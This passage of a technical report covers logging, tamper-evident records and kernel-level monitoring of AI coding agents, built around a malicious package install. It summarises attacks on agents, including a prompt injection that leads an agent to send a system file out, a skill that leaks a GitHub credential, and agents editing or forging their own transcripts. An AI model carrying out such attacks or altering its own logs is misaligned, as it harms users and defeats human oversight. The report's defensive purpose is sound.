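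Hashes work better for finding exact copies across sessions. If the tidewatch README turns out to be malicious, a search for `9c41d2…` lists every session in which an agent read an identical file. Agent instruction files do get copied between projects. In *A Deterministic Control Plane for LLM Coding Agents*, Madatha (2026) examined 6,145 agent configuration files from a study of 10,008 public GitHub repositories. After adjusting for forks (deliberate copies of a whole repository), he found that 10.1% of the files were exact duplicates across independent repositories, and that 75.5% of the matching pairs belonged to different organisations. Changing one character of a file changes its hash, so a team needs the saved text to find near-copies.

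For most companies, the best choice is to keep both the text and its hash for a limited time, then delete the text. The hash stays in the event log, and the text goes into a separate store under that hash. If 50 agents read the same README, the store needs only one copy.

It also matters which version of a web page the recorder hashes, because a harness may convert the page to plain text, shorten it or have another model summarise it before the main model receives it. A hash of the raw download will match an archived copy, but the model may not have received everything in that download, such as an instruction hidden in the page's code. A hash of the converted text identifies what the model received, but an outsider can't easily reproduce it. The safest record has both hashes, each labelled.

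### How much data this produces

Suppose a company has 200 developers who each run 20 agent sessions a day, with 150 events per session and 1.5 kB per event. That makes 600,000 events and about 0.9 GB a day, or roughly 225 GB over a year of 250 working days. A company should replace these assumptions with its own counts after a week or two.

Saved text adds at most another 0.8 GB a day if the agent reads ten files or pages in each session and they average 20 kB. Ninety days of text would take up no more than 72 GB, and less once the store removes duplicates.

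The number of events is the assumption most likely to be wrong, because a large install can start hundreds of processes and open thousands of files. If logging every file that the installed code opens raises the average session to 2,000 events, the daily total becomes 12 GB. A sensible compromise is to record every process start and outgoing connection, but only file reads in sensitive places, such as folders containing keys.

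Engineers who monitor performance often keep only a sample of their records to save money. That works for measuring average speed, but a company that kept one session in ten would probably have no record of the tidewatch install. The full records take up only about 1 GB a day, so there is little reason to take that risk.

### Secrets, personal data and retention

A log this detailed becomes a target. It can capture passwords that developers paste into requests, configuration files that agents print, and usernames and passwords in the addresses of private package indexes. Even public instruction files can contain secrets. Madatha reports a 3.18% hit rate for credential patterns in his sample, though some matches may be placeholders. The log also records in detail how each employee works.

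OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans*, a widely used set of names for logging model calls, leaves instructions, inputs and outputs out of the log by default. For production systems where volume or sensitive data is a concern, it recommends keeping this content in external storage with its own access rules and logging only a reference to it. Sharif forbids raw inputs and outputs in audit entries altogether. A company that needs them for debugging must keep them in a separate system, linked by the entry's ID.

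Redaction, the removal of secrets before anything reaches the log, makes logging safer but can destroy evidence. Masking an entire address that contains a password would hide which index supplied the package, so it is better to remove only the password and keep the server's name and path. Some redaction tools mask any long random-looking string, including file hashes, so a team should exempt the hash fields. A redacted copy also no longer matches the hash of the original, so the record needs to state which version each hash describes.

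Replacing a secret with a hash can still expose it if the secret is easy to guess. Sharif's format has an optional fingerprint, a hash of the full content before redaction. If the redacted part is a short password, someone with the rest of the page can try likely passwords until the hash matches. Sharif's draft states that nobody can reverse the fingerprint to recover the data, which is true for long, unpredictable text but not for a short password. A keyed hash, which requires a secret key to compute, prevents this guessing as long as the key is stored elsewhere, and it still shows when the same credential appears twice.

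Published rules give some guidance on how long to keep the log. Birkholz, Heldt and Steele (2026), in *Verifiable Agent Conversation Records*, another proposal submitted to the IETF, compared the minimum periods in several frameworks:

| Framework | Minimum retention for logs |
|---|---|
| EU AI Act, high-risk systems | 6 months, longer for some financial services |
| PCI DSS, for payment cards | 12 months, with 3 months available immediately |
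| FedRAMP, for US government cloud services | 12 months in active storage, then 18 months in cold storage |

They recommend at least 12 months, because that meets the most common threshold. Sharif recommends 12 months for high-risk systems and 6 for others. His draft gives August 2026 as the start of the EU's logging duty for high-risk systems. However, an amendment has moved the high-risk duties to December 2027 and August 2028, according to the National Law Review's *EU Digital Omnibus on AI Enters Into Force* (2026). An agent that sets up software projects may not count as high-risk.

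These periods apply to logs, and page text can have a shorter one. A reasonable starting point is to keep events and hashes for 12 months and redacted text for 90 days, or longer if the text comes from a session under investigation. The 90 days is a judgement about how long people usually take to discover a malicious package. A company that tends to learn of such packages later should keep the text for longer. Birkholz and colleagues add that a company should control who can read the logs, and that providing logs to authorities under the EU Act calls for a record of who read them.

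### Making changes to the log detectable

The agent, the harness and the installed code usually share the developer's account, so any of them may be able to edit the transcript. An attacker's package could delete event 8, and an employee hiding a mistake could change "approval skipped" to "approval given".

The basic protection is append-only storage, which lets users add entries but not alter or delete them. It should run on a different machine, under an account that the developer and the agent can't use. The laptop should send entries there within seconds, because they can be altered or deleted until they arrive.

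Hashing can reveal changes that storage rules fail to prevent, but storing a separate hash beside each line detects little beyond accidental damage. Someone who changes "skipped" to "given" in event 4 can compute a new hash for the new line, and the log will look correct. If they delete event 8 together with its hash, nothing in the log will show the deletion, because no other line depends on it.

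In a hash chain, each entry includes the hash of the entry before it. Sharif defines the link as follows:

`prev_hash(N) = hex(SHA-256(JCS(record(N-1))))`

JCS writes the previous entry in a standard form, so the same data always produces the same bytes. SHA-256 hashes those bytes, and "hex" writes the hash as 64 characters. The previous entry contains the hash of the entry before it, so each hash depends on everything that came earlier. If someone edits event 4, its hash no longer matches the value saved in event 5. If someone deletes event 8, event 9 points to a missing entry.

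A chain alone has two weaknesses. Anyone who can rewrite the whole file can edit event 4 and recompute every later link. Anyone who can cut off the end can remove events 8 to 10, and the remaining seven will still pass the check. Both attacks fail if a copy of the latest hash is stored where the attacker can't reach it, because the rewritten or shortened log won't match it. Sharif's format ends each session with an entry that contains the number of records and a combined hash, and he recommends storing the combined hash in a separate append-only system. An entry can also carry a digital signature, which helps only if the signing key isn't on the machine the attacker controls.

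Madatha traces the technique to work by Haber and Stornetta in 1991 and to Certificate Transparency, a large public system that records the certificates websites use to prove their identity. There, the technique lets auditors check the log later without trusting the server that holds it. But a chain shows only that nobody changed the entries after the recorder wrote them. If the recorder missed the connection in event 8 or wrote down a false address, the chain will preserve the error. Sharif therefore treats a log that an agent writes about itself as weaker evidence and recommends a separate recorder for deployments with higher security requirements.

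Chains also complicate privacy requests, because deleting an entry breaks the next link. Sharif's solution is to replace the deleted entry with a tombstone that keeps the entry's ID, time and original hash, so a checker can accept the gap. Somebody could then remove evidence and call it a privacy request, so the company should record who approved each deletion. The separate text store avoids most of the problem, because the chain contains only the hash of a saved README and the company can delete the README without changing the chain.

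### What the published formats leave out

A company can use a published log format, but these formats mostly cover conversations and tool calls, with little about the pages and packages that agents fetch and install. The example record shows the differences.

By default, OpenTelemetry would record event 4 as a tool execution, with the tool's name and, if available, the call ID. It would include the pip command only if the developer had opted in to recording arguments, and the README's text only if they had opted in to recording results. The result field is meant only for successful calls, so it would leave out failed installs, which may already have run a package's code. The tool entry has no dedicated field for a redirect, a page hash or a package digest. The section on external storage still has a "TODO" where a common way to refer to saved content should be.

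These conventions are also still changing. OpenTelemetry's *Generative AI semantic conventions* page now redirects to a separate repository, which still labels the conventions as in development, according to TrueFoundry, a company that sells AI infrastructure. TruLens, a tool for evaluating AI applications, uses its own fields for details such as the editor version and workspace because, according to its *Semantic Conventions*, OpenTelemetry has no convention for coding agents.

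Sharif's format is better for establishing the order of events and detecting tampering, but it records less of what each event contained. Event 4 would contain the tool's name and a hash of its parameters. An investigator who already suspected the exact command could hash it and compare, but couldn't search for every command that mentioned `pkgs.example.net`. The format allows extra fields but bans raw inputs, so it's unclear whether a full URL would be acceptable.

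Birkholz and colleagues instead keep the full input and output of each tool call, along with the model, the harness version and the git commit. Their draft format would preserve the command and the README's text, but it would capture the package's version and source only if pip printed them. A signature and an optional hash cover the whole session record. They can show that the record hasn't changed since signing, but the format has no separate hash for comparing one page across sessions. This version of the draft expired on 29 August 2026.

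Security teams may prefer the Open Cybersecurity Schema Framework (OCSF), a common format for security events. According to AWS, version 1.8.0, released in March 2026, added an AI profile with details of the model, its token usage and the roles of messages. The details AWS lists don't identify the text the model read. lmodel's documentation lists process activity among the events that can carry this profile, which suits events 5 and 7. *AOS tracing with OCSF*, from OWASP, a software security non-profit, instead records an agent's tool use as API activity.

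| Format | What it keeps about a tool call | What it lacks about fetched resources |
|---|---|---|
| OpenTelemetry | Tool name and call ID; arguments and results if the developer opts in | Dedicated fields for redirects, page hashes and package digests |
| Sharif | Tool name, hashes of parameters and response, position in the chain | The text itself; fields for the page's URL, redirects and package digest |
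| Birkholz and colleagues | Full input and output | A separate hash and redirect history for each page; dedicated package fields |
| OCSF with the AI profile | Model, token and message data attached to a security event | The text the model read and its hash |

The format of Birkholz and colleagues needs the least adaptation for a company starting now, because it keeps the text and explicitly accepts extra fields. The company would have to add the redirects, page hashes, package details and approval status, remove secrets before writing anything, and move long texts to the separate store. If the company already sends its logs to an OpenTelemetry or OCSF system, it can add the same fields there under its own names, but should expect to rename them later.

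## Recording inside the agent program

The harness takes part directly in six of the ten events in the tidewatch record: the request, the two texts the agent read, the tool call, its result and the closing reply. It can supply records of these events in three ways. It keeps a transcript on disk, it can export telemetry, which consists of structured records that it streams to a server, and it can call hooks, which are small programs that run at set points, such as before or after a tool call.

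### The transcript on disk

Claude Code saves a transcript of each session as a text file in the user's home folder so the user can resume the session later. According to Anthropic, which makes Claude Code, the transcript includes anything that passes through a tool, such as file contents, command output and pasted text. For the tidewatch session, it would contain the README, the installation guide as the model received it, and whatever pip printed. The transcript isn't encrypted, and only the operating system's file permissions protect it. If the agent opens a file of passwords, the transcript will contain them in readable form.

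Claude Code deletes transcripts after 30 days by default, so a company that heard about the malicious `harbour-utils` six weeks after the install would find no transcript of it on the laptop. Administrators can lengthen the period, and transcripts from the desktop app stay until someone sets a limit. But a user can switch transcripts off, or delete a project's transcripts with one command. Anthropic keeps commercial customers' data on its own servers for 30 days as standard, or not at all under a zero-retention agreement. A company that wants to keep the text for 90 days should copy it off the laptop.

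Codex CLI writes a similar file. Vaughan's *Observability & Debugging*, from an independent blog about the program, describes it as a complete record of every prompt, model response and tool call.

Transcripts are an awkward basis for monitoring because vendors design them for their own programs to read. Anthropic warns that the format of Claude Code's transcripts changes between versions, so any release can break a program that depends on it.

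### Exported telemetry

Telemetry suits central monitoring better, because the harness sends it to a server while the session is still running. Claude Code and Codex CLI both use OpenTelemetry's protocols, and both leave the export off until someone configures it. Claude Code users set one variable to enable telemetry and others to choose where it goes, according to Anthropic's *Monitoring*. Codex CLI users configure it in the `[otel]` section of a configuration file, as AWS's *Set up OpenTelemetry for OpenAI Codex* explains.

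Anthropic says Claude Code can export metrics, log events and traces. Metrics count things like cost and sessions, so a company that collects only metrics won't see the commands the agent runs. Log events describe each prompt, model request and tool result. Traces, still in beta, group each prompt with the model requests and tool calls that followed it.

Like OpenTelemetry's own conventions, the log events leave out content by default. Event 4 of the tidewatch record would reach the server as a successful use of the shell tool, with its duration and the size of its input and output, but without the pip command. Four further settings add the content:

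| Claude Code setting | What it adds |
|---|---|
| `OTEL_LOG_USER_PROMPTS` | The text of the user's requests and, unless a separate setting prevents it, the model's replies |
| `OTEL_LOG_TOOL_DETAILS` | Full shell commands, other tool arguments such as URLs, error messages, and the names of third-party plugins |
| `OTEL_LOG_TOOL_CONTENT` | The text that tools returned, if traces are on |
| `OTEL_LOG_RAW_API_BODIES` | Each complete request to the model and each response |

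Some of this content arrives shortened. Anthropic's documentation gives a limit of 512 characters for a single value in the general list of tool arguments, so the end of a long URL can be cut off. The limit for returned text is 60 KB. If the tool call ends in an error, no returned text arrives, so the output of a failed install may be missing even though the package's code has already run. The error message appears separately if tool details are on.

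The last setting comes closest to showing what the model read, because it captures the text after the harness has converted or shortened it. It also produces much more data, since successive requests repeat much of the same conversation. Claude Code can write these requests to local files without the 60 KB limit, but the files then have to be sent off the machine separately.

Codex CLI has a different default from Claude Code. *Codex CLI Observability* (Vaughan, 2026) lists an event for each approval decision and another for each tool result, with an excerpt of the output. The user's prompt stays hidden unless someone chooses to export it. But tool results are exported even when prompts aren't, and they can include the contents of sensitive files (Vaughan, 2026, *Codex CLI OpenTelemetry*). Vaughan recommends a filter that removes known kinds of keys before the data goes to an outside service.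 A company that moves from Claude Code to Codex CLI with the same privacy assumptions could therefore export text it meant to keep private.

Vaughan's description of the tool-result event doesn't mention the command itself, so a company should run a known install and check whether the full command appears in the logs. This check also shows whether the company will see URLs. Li, Huang and colleagues (2026) found in *Ring-0 by Default* that the version of Codex CLI they tested had no fetch tool of its own, so the model opened URLs through shell commands.

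### Who controls the settings

On a company laptop, the telemetry settings belong in managed settings, the central configuration that overrides a developer's own. If administrators set the server's address there, Claude Code removes any conflicting addresses the developer has set.

According to Anthropic, a project's settings file can't turn telemetry on or send it somewhere else, but it can turn an exporter off unless a higher-priority setting prevents this. The project in the tidewatch example came from outside the company, so administrators should set the choice of exporter centrally as well as the address.

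Several other gaps are easy to miss:

- Claude Code's events don't name the machine. An administrator can add a name as a custom attribute, but if a value contains a space, Claude Code leaves all the custom attributes off its events and reports no error.
- Sessions that run in Anthropic's cloud don't read the managed settings file on a developer's laptop, so they need their own configuration.
- Codex CLI lets users switch between named sets of options, called profiles in OpenAI's *Advanced Configuration*. Telemetry settings can differ between profiles, so a test of one profile doesn't cover the rest.

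These settings also change quickly. AWS checked the instructions in *Analyzing OpenAI Codex Usage with CloudWatch and OpenTelemetry* against one version of Codex CLI and warns that names may differ in others. Claude Code recently stopped sending an event that, among other things, counted the network connections its sandbox had refused, so any alert built on that event would have stopped firing.

### Hooks

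A hook lets a company run its own code inside the session. When the agent asks to run the pip command in event 4, Claude Code first sends a description of the tool call to any hook registered for that point. The hook can record the call, refuse it or do nothing. If it does nothing, the normal approval rules apply. After the command finishes, Claude Code calls a second set of hooks. Successful and failed calls trigger different events, so a recorder should register for both.

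Hooks have two advantages over telemetry for recording installs. First, they can record an install before it starts. Anthropic's documentation describes a type of hook that sends each event to a web address, so an entry for the pip command can reach another machine before pip runs. This meets the requirement in Sharif's log format that a policy decision be logged before the action. Second, a hook can collect facts the harness doesn't export, such as a README's hash or the project's git commit. It can also check a package's name or source before the install.

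Claude Code runs the same hooks when the main agent hands part of a task to a subagent, a helper with its own conversation, and passes the subagent's ID to the hooks. Administrators can block all hooks except those they manage, and a developer's own settings can't disable the managed ones.

A hook can still fail to stop a command. If it relies on an MCP server that isn't connected, Claude Code reports an error and continues. Anthropic also describes the filter that selects which shell commands trigger a hook as best-effort. It recommends the permission system for rules that must always hold. A recorder can avoid this filter by receiving all shell commands and sorting them later.

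Code that runs outside a tool call is harder to catch. *What we learned about AI agent security by monitoring our agents*, by Levine, Lejeail and Mooney, describes a malicious skill for Claude Code. Datadog's researchers found the skill and reproduced it in a controlled test. It contained commands that the harness ran while preparing the skill's text, before the model received it. The model refused to use the skill, but the commands had already sent a GitHub credential to the attacker. A record of the model's inputs and outputs would have shown only the refusal. The three work for Datadog, which sells a product for monitoring agents, but the test supports their narrower point that such a record can miss code the harness runs by itself.

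### How the harnesses compare

Hooks are the most widely available of the three sources. Vaughan lists hook points in Codex CLI before and after each tool call. Elastic, a search and security software company, has published a method for auditing Cursor through Cursor's hooks, and open-source recorders can attach to Copilot through hooks too. The table is current as of autumn 2026, except where it gives an earlier date.

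| Harness | Recorded by default | Must be switched on | Full commands and URLs | How long local records last |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code (Anthropic, October and November 2026) | Transcript on disk, in plain text | Telemetry, then separate settings for prompts, commands and returned text; hooks | In the transcript; in telemetry only with tool details on | 30 days; desktop sessions until someone sets a limit |
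| Codex CLI (Vaughan, March and April 2026; AWS, August 2026) | Transcript on disk | Telemetry, with a separate setting for prompts; hooks | In the transcript's tool calls; confirm for telemetry | Confirm on the installed version |
| Cursor (Elastic, undated) | Confirm on the installed version | Hooks | Confirm with a trial install | Confirm on the installed version |
| Copilot | Confirm on the installed version | Hooks | Confirm with a trial install | Confirm on the installed version |

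A trial install takes a few minutes. The tester asks the agent to install a harmless package from a test index with a long, distinctive address, then searches the transcript and the central log for that address. Repeating the test with an install that fails shows whether failed installs also leave a complete record.

### Reading several harnesses at once

Developers in one company often use several harnesses, which use different names for the same facts. Even the session ID's field name varies by vendor, according to OpenLIT, an open-source monitoring project that maintains a separate adapter for each harness. A collector translates these formats into one, so a single search covers all of them.

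Perplexity, an AI search company, publishes an open-source collector called numbat. McRee (2026) tried it in *numbat*, written for the SANS Internet Storm Center, which reports on security threats and tools. Numbat runs on macOS, Linux and Windows, and collects data from hooks and plugins, exported OpenTelemetry logs, and session files already on disk.

McRee first ran a command that listed the agents on his computer, the session files available for each, and whether numbat had a hook in place for it. He regularly uses products from Anthropic, OpenAI and Google, but the number of agents installed still surprised him. Levine and her colleagues found a similar problem at Datadog, where some applications contacted model providers directly and so didn't show up in the approved gateway's traffic. A company needs a list of its agents to know what share of them it monitors.

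McRee then installed numbat's hooks for Claude Code and Gemini and set them to save everything. By default, numbat writes its results to a file in the user's home folder, with one JSON record per line. The file contains events, findings from its detection rules, and any decisions to block an action. To test a rule, he asked Claude Code to scan a network, and numbat recorded a finding. Unless an administrator turns on blocking, numbat reports such actions without stopping them.

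For an investigation, numbat can arrange a session's events into a timeline and package the evidence with a list of file hashes. According to Open Source For You, it can build the timeline from saved session files even if nobody had installed numbat before the incident. This would help a company that had no monitoring in place during the tidewatch install and started looking into it three days later.

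These features depend on the records the harness kept. If Claude Code deleted a transcript after 30 days, numbat can't read it. The hashes in an evidence package can reveal changes made after numbat created the package, but not earlier edits to the transcript. The results file is also under the developer's account by default, so a company should use numbat's option to send records to a server.

McRee's review is weak evidence of how well numbat detects unsafe installs. He chose a rule he expected to be easy to trigger, and he didn't report a test with a malicious package or count false alarms. It is more useful as a demonstration that one program can collect these records from different harnesses.

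McRee took up the tool after OpenAI agents broke into Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models, in July 2026. He writes that real-time monitoring of agents' actions isn't yet standard practice, even at the laboratories that build them, but he doesn't cite any laboratory's own account of its monitoring.

### What the harness adds to the worked record

If the tidewatch session ran in Claude Code with the content settings on, the harness could supply the following parts of the ten-event record:

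| Event | What Claude Code can supply | What is missing |
|---|---|---|
| 1. Request | Session ID, user, request text, repository address | Machine name, unless the company adds it; git commit, unless a hook reads it |
| 2. File read | Path and text of the README | Hash, unless a hook computes it |
| 3. Page fetched | Requested URL and the text returned | Hash and a separate field for the redirect |
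| 4. Tool call | Full command, call ID, approval source and permission mode | Nothing essential |
| 5. Process start | No process details | Process number and ancestry |
| 6. Package download | Whatever pip printed | A reliable index address and file digest |
| 7. Install-time code | No details | The program that ran |
| 8. Connection | No details | Destination and bytes sent |
| 9. Tool result | Success or failure, duration, output | Exit code as a separate field |
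| 10. Reply | Text of the reply | Nothing essential |

In the approval fields of event 4, Claude Code uses the source value `config` for any decision it made without asking, whether because of a saved rule, a company policy or a mode that skips approval. Recent versions also record the permission mode, and the value `bypassPermissions` means the session was running with approval switched off. If the user refuses a command, Claude Code records the decision but no tool result, so a log of results alone would omit every install that a user refused.

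This layer is mainly useful because it connects events 1 to 4. Claude Code gives every event that follows a user's prompt the same prompt ID, and gives each tool call an ID that hooks also receive. An investigator can start from the pip command, find the request that led to it, and search what the agent read in between for `pkgs.example.net`.

Other security tools usually can't connect an agent's action to what led to it. Elastic points out that an agent's commands look the same as the developer's to endpoint security software. Levine and her colleagues had a similar problem with application logs, which could show an agent's final request to another service without the prompt, document or tool result that led to it.

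A text search won't always find the source. If a README tells the agent to run a Makefile and the Makefile contains the index address, the address may never appear in the agent's command. An agent may also combine instructions from two pages or reword them. Li and colleagues say that reliably linking each action to the input that caused it is one of the problems still to solve.

### When the agent can edit its own log

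The main objection to relying on these records is that the program under investigation writes them. A harness keeps its transcript in the user's files, which the agent's own tools can usually reach, whereas an operating system keeps its audit log where ordinary programs can't change it.

Li and colleagues tested this problem in Claude Code, Codex CLI and Gemini CLI, Google's coding agent. They ran each harness in a fresh container and replaced the model with a script that issued tool calls, which showed what the harness would allow regardless of a model's judgement. With approval switched off, Claude Code and Codex CLI both allowed changes to their own transcripts. Gemini CLI blocked them, but only through a general filter on shell commands, not a specific protection for the transcript.

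They also added a false entry to saved sessions and then resumed the sessions. When the entry had the right format, each of the three harnesses accepted it as a message from the user in all eight of its runs. A transcript can therefore contain a request the developer never made, and without another record of the conversation, the developer may have no way to prove that to an investigator.

The experiments show what the harnesses permit, but they don't measure how often agents alter their records in practice. Li and colleagues tested one version of each program and told the vendors about the results, so later versions may behave differently. They don't consider the false entries an exploit, because creating one requires permission to change the user's files. However, install-time code usually has that permission.

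The best response is to send each event immediately to append-only storage on another machine. A hook can send it before the tool call, and telemetry can follow within seconds if the company sets a short export interval. The laptop's login to that storage should not have permission to read entries, because the agent may be able to use the same login.

Fast delivery doesn't help if the harness never sends the event, or sends a false one. The company also needs a record from a program outside the harness, such as the operating system's list of started processes. If that list shows pip starting at 09:14:21 and the harness sent no tool-call event around that time, the harness's record is incomplete.

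A mismatch can have causes other than tampering. The developer may have typed the pip command in another window, or the telemetry may have failed because its login to the server expired. In Claude Code, if the script that supplies this login fails, the export stops until the script works again. The process record can help distinguish these cases because it shows whether the harness or the developer's own terminal started pip.

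## Recording from outside: processes, network and registries

Claude Code's own records cover the start of the tidewatch install well but contain almost nothing about what pip did once it started. That part of the install leaves traces in three places the agent doesn't write to. The operating system reports which programs start, which files they write and which connections they open. Firewalls and proxies record the traffic that leaves the laptop. The company's package index logs each request it receives.

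### What the operating system reports

A harness has to go through the kernel, the core of the operating system, to create a process, so the kernel can report the new process even if the harness logs nothing. Most companies collect these reports with endpoint security software, which runs with administrator rights and sends events to a central server. On Windows, the security log can record each new process and its parent as event 4688.

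On Linux, many products use eBPF, which runs small monitoring programs inside the kernel. An administrator attaches each one to a type of event, such as a program starting. The kernel checks that the monitoring program will finish and use only valid memory, then runs it each time the event occurs.

For the tidewatch install, the operating system could report the following:

| Time (UTC) | Report |
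|---|---|
| 09:14:21 | The harness (3990) starts a shell (4118), which starts pip (4120) |
| 09:14:24 | pip connects to the package servers and writes the downloaded archive to a temporary folder |
| 09:14:26 | pip starts Python (4131) to run `setup.py` |
| 09:14:27 | Process 4131 opens a connection to an IP address on port 443 |
| 09:14:33 | pip ends with exit code 0 |

The connection report contains an IP address instead of the name `metrics.example.org`. To recover the name, the software has to match the address with a recent DNS lookup, the request that turns a server's name into an address. The reports also contain nothing about the README or the developer's request. *ADR* (2026), which describes a detection system for agents, points out the same limitation in endpoint tools.

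Companies should check that their software saves each program's full command line. Windows leaves the command line out of event 4688 unless an administrator enables it. Without it, the record would show that pip ran but not that the command named `pkgs.example.net`. Dedicated security products can have the same gap. When Elastic investigated a Claude Code session from July 2026, its telemetry had no arguments for a program that had opened a tunnel to the internet, so its analysts had to reconstruct a typical command.

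These reports accumulate quickly. *AI coding agents are running on your machines* (Hernández and Lo Prete, 2026) describes a session in which an agent ran five commands in ten seconds and the kernel reported 64 program starts. *On the Effectiveness of Kernel-Level Evidence for Agent Security* (King, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) covers a larger set of recorded sessions, which averaged about 3,500 events each, including file and network activity. At that rate, the company with 4,000 sessions a day would produce 14 million events a day, or about 21 GB at 1.5 kB each, which is another reason to record only selected file events.

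### Tracing pip back to the agent

Process ancestry shows whether an agent or a developer started pip. An investigator can trace the suspicious connection back from Python (PID 4131) through pip (4120) and the shell (4118) to the harness (3990). Pandex's planted packages also used process ancestry to report which agents had installed them.

The investigator also has to recognise the harness. Hernández and Lo Prete of the security company Sysdig found that Claude Code, Gemini CLI and Codex CLI each need a different rule. Claude Code runs as a program built with Bun, a JavaScript runtime, and Codex CLI runs as a standalone program with its own path. Gemini CLI runs inside the computer's shared copy of Node.js, so a rule that matches only Node.js would also match many unrelated programs. The full path of a parent program can help. HawkinsOperations, a personal site on threat hunting, traced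 a PowerShell window on Windows to Codex CLI because the parent's path included the folder of OpenAI's npm package.

A rule that checks only a process's immediate parent will usually find a shell. Elastic has published a rule that compares all of a process's ancestors with a list of known AI tools, so it works even when there are several shells in between. Saving the whole chain is also useful because one agent can run another. According to DTEX's *Hermes AI Agent Detection and the End of Claude’s Dominance*, Hermes uses Claude Code as a subprocess for coding. A record of only the nearest harness would include Claude Code but omit Hermes, which was directing it.

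Tracing a process's ancestors won't lead back to the agent if another program has taken over the work. In Elastic's July case, shells under Claude Code set up background jobs that macOS starts automatically. A tunnelling program on the same computer first appeared under a shell and later under `launchd`, the macOS service that starts such jobs. Tracing the later process's ancestors would end at `launchd`.

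VS Code runs extensions in a separate process, so process ancestry may not distinguish an agent extension's commands from those of an ordinary extension. Agents in containers or in Windows Subsystem for Linux, which runs Linux programs on a Windows machine, may not appear in the host's process records at all. *Detecting Shadow AI* (Canale and Soulis, 2026) treats these environments as outside the reach of its Windows detector. A company that allows these environments needs a separate sensor inside them.

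Agents repeatedly contact a server and run shell commands, but Canale and Soulis point out that `npm install` does too, so this behaviour alone doesn't identify an agent. They built "behavioural twins", pairs of programs with the same processes and connections, in which one contacts a model and the other an ordinary service. A rule that ignores which service a program contacts can't tell the twins apart.

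Canale and Soulis ran 12 artificial agents, 3 other AI components and 9 harmless workloads five times on one computer. Two behavioural rules flagged every harmless twin. Their own detector, which also checks whether the process contacts a known model service, flagged none of the twins and found every agent in most runs. But it runs only once an hour, and it caught an intermittent agent in about one scan in three. The tidewatch session lasted 34 seconds, so an hourly scan would probably miss it. Such scans are useful for listing the agents on a company's computers, but recording installs requires continuous collection.

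Finding an agent among a command's ancestor processes doesn't show whether the command was harmful or safe. Sophos' *When AI agents look like attackers*, which examines a week of Windows telemetry from June 2026, describes a case where Codex tried to download a Python installer from Python's official site. The security software blocked its first method because attackers often use it, then blocked the second method Codex tried. Sophos considers much of what it found benign but still wants some of the detection rules to keep firing, because the actions are risky whoever starts them.

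### Joining kernel events to the model's activity

Process ancestry can connect an install to a harness, but not to the particular model response that led to it, and a long session may contain dozens of responses. *AgentSight* (Zheng, Yu and colleagues, 2025) tries to identify that response by using eBPF to collect two streams of evidence. One contains the harness's exchanges with the model, copied from the encryption library before outgoing text is encrypted and after replies are decrypted. The other contains process starts, file activity and connections.

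AgentSight matches actions to model responses by checking whether the process descends from the agent, whether the action came shortly after a response (the window is 100 to 500 milliseconds), and whether text from the response appears in the action's arguments. In the tidewatch install, the address `pkgs.example.net` would appear in both the model's response and pip's command line. A second language model then checks the combined record for suspicious behaviour.

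Zheng and colleagues tested this on an agent asked to clone and build a C project. The project's README directed the agent to a web page with a hidden instruction, and the agent read a system file and sent it to an outside server. AgentSight reduced 521 events to 37, and the second model identified the attack. The test shows that the design can reconstruct such a sequence of events, but one success isn't enough to estimate a detection or false-alarm rate.

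The clues become less useful if the harmful action happens later. Suppose the setup code in `harbour-utils` had written a script and scheduled it for the next night. The system's scheduler would start the script long after the 500 milliseconds had passed, and the new process would not descend from the agent.

*AgentLoupe* (Bao, Liu and colleagues, 2026) addresses this by labelling whatever the agent touches. When it detects a prompt to a model, it assigns a number to the part of the harness that sent the prompt. Any process that the harness then starts inherits the number. If one of those processes writes a file, the file gets the number too, as does any process that later opens it. The scheduled script would therefore still carry the number of the exchange that led to the install.

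AgentLoupe starts a new number with each independent prompt and keeps a link to the old one, which stops labels from spreading to everything on the computer. In one of Bao and colleagues' two tests, a session wrote a malicious instruction into AGENTS.md and a later session obeyed it. AgentLoupe connected the two sessions through the file. In the other test, it traced a scheduled connection to an attacker's server back to the original exchange. Bao and colleagues haven't measured how often their labels create false links or miss real ones.

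*Agent-Warden* (Cui, Gu and colleagues, 2026) follows processes and files in a similar way but doesn't read the model's traffic. This avoids collecting prompts, but it can trace an action only to the agent, not to a particular response. It doesn't cover network connections. Its labels disappear after a restart, and may also disappear when the computer runs short of memory.

| System | Slowdown in its own tests | Evidence that it traces actions correctly |
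|---|---|---|
| AgentSight | 0.4% to 4.9%, depending on the task | One prompt-injection case |
| AgentLoupe | 4.5% to 8.0% | Two delayed or cross-session attacks |
| Agent-Warden | 0.2% to 3.5% | One prepared scenario, traced correctly in all 120 runs |

This overhead looks acceptable for most development work, but the tests used different tasks and computers, so the percentages can't be used to rank the systems. The AgentSight figures come from only three runs of each task, and the AgentLoupe figures from only five. All the tests ran on Linux, so the designs are easier to try on build servers than on Windows or macOS laptops. AgentSight and AgentLoupe collect prompts in readable form, so their records need the same protection as a transcript.

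### How much kernel evidence improves detection

King and colleagues provide the best evidence on whether kernel records help detect attacks. They collected kernel and application records from 4,047 agent sessions, each run in its own container. The application records included the prompt, tool descriptions and transcript. Some sessions contained attacks, such as a tampered MCP server that read credentials. The researchers collected the kernel records with strace, a standard Linux tool for recording a program's requests to the kernel, instead of eBPF.

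They then trained or prompted ten detectors and measured each one's AUROC, the probability that a detector scores a randomly chosen malicious session higher than a randomly chosen harmless one. Guessing would score 0.5 and a perfect detector 1. In the most realistic test, the attacks came from families that were absent from the detectors' training data or examples.

| Detector | Evidence | AUROC on unfamiliar attack families |
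|---|---|---|
| Falco's default rules | Kernel | 0.572 |
| XGBoost, a conventional machine-learning method | Kernel | 0.750 |
| XGBoost | Kernel and application | 0.850 |
| Llama-3.1-8B, trained for this task | Kernel | 0.922 |

Falco, a widely used open-source tool, applies rules to kernel events. Its default rules did little better than guessing, which suggests that a company can't just install a tool designed for servers and expect it to recognise an agent under attack. Seven of the ten detectors performed best when the two kinds of evidence were combined.

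Combining kernel and application evidence helps because some attacks appear in only one of them. When a tool secretly read credentials and copied them to a log, detectors averaged 0.976 with kernel evidence and 0.586 with application evidence. When an attack changed the text an agent retrieved, they averaged 0.703 with kernel evidence and 0.906 with application evidence. Both comparisons come from an easier test in which the training data included the same types of attack.

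A detector with a high AUROC can still raise too many alerts. If it wrongly flags 1% of harmless sessions, it produces about 40 false alarms a day at 4,000 sessions a day. Detectors can also overfit to one harness. When King and colleagues tried a different agent and harness, one detector's AUROC fell to 0.662, largely because it had relied on temporary files that Claude Code writes and the new harness usually didn't.

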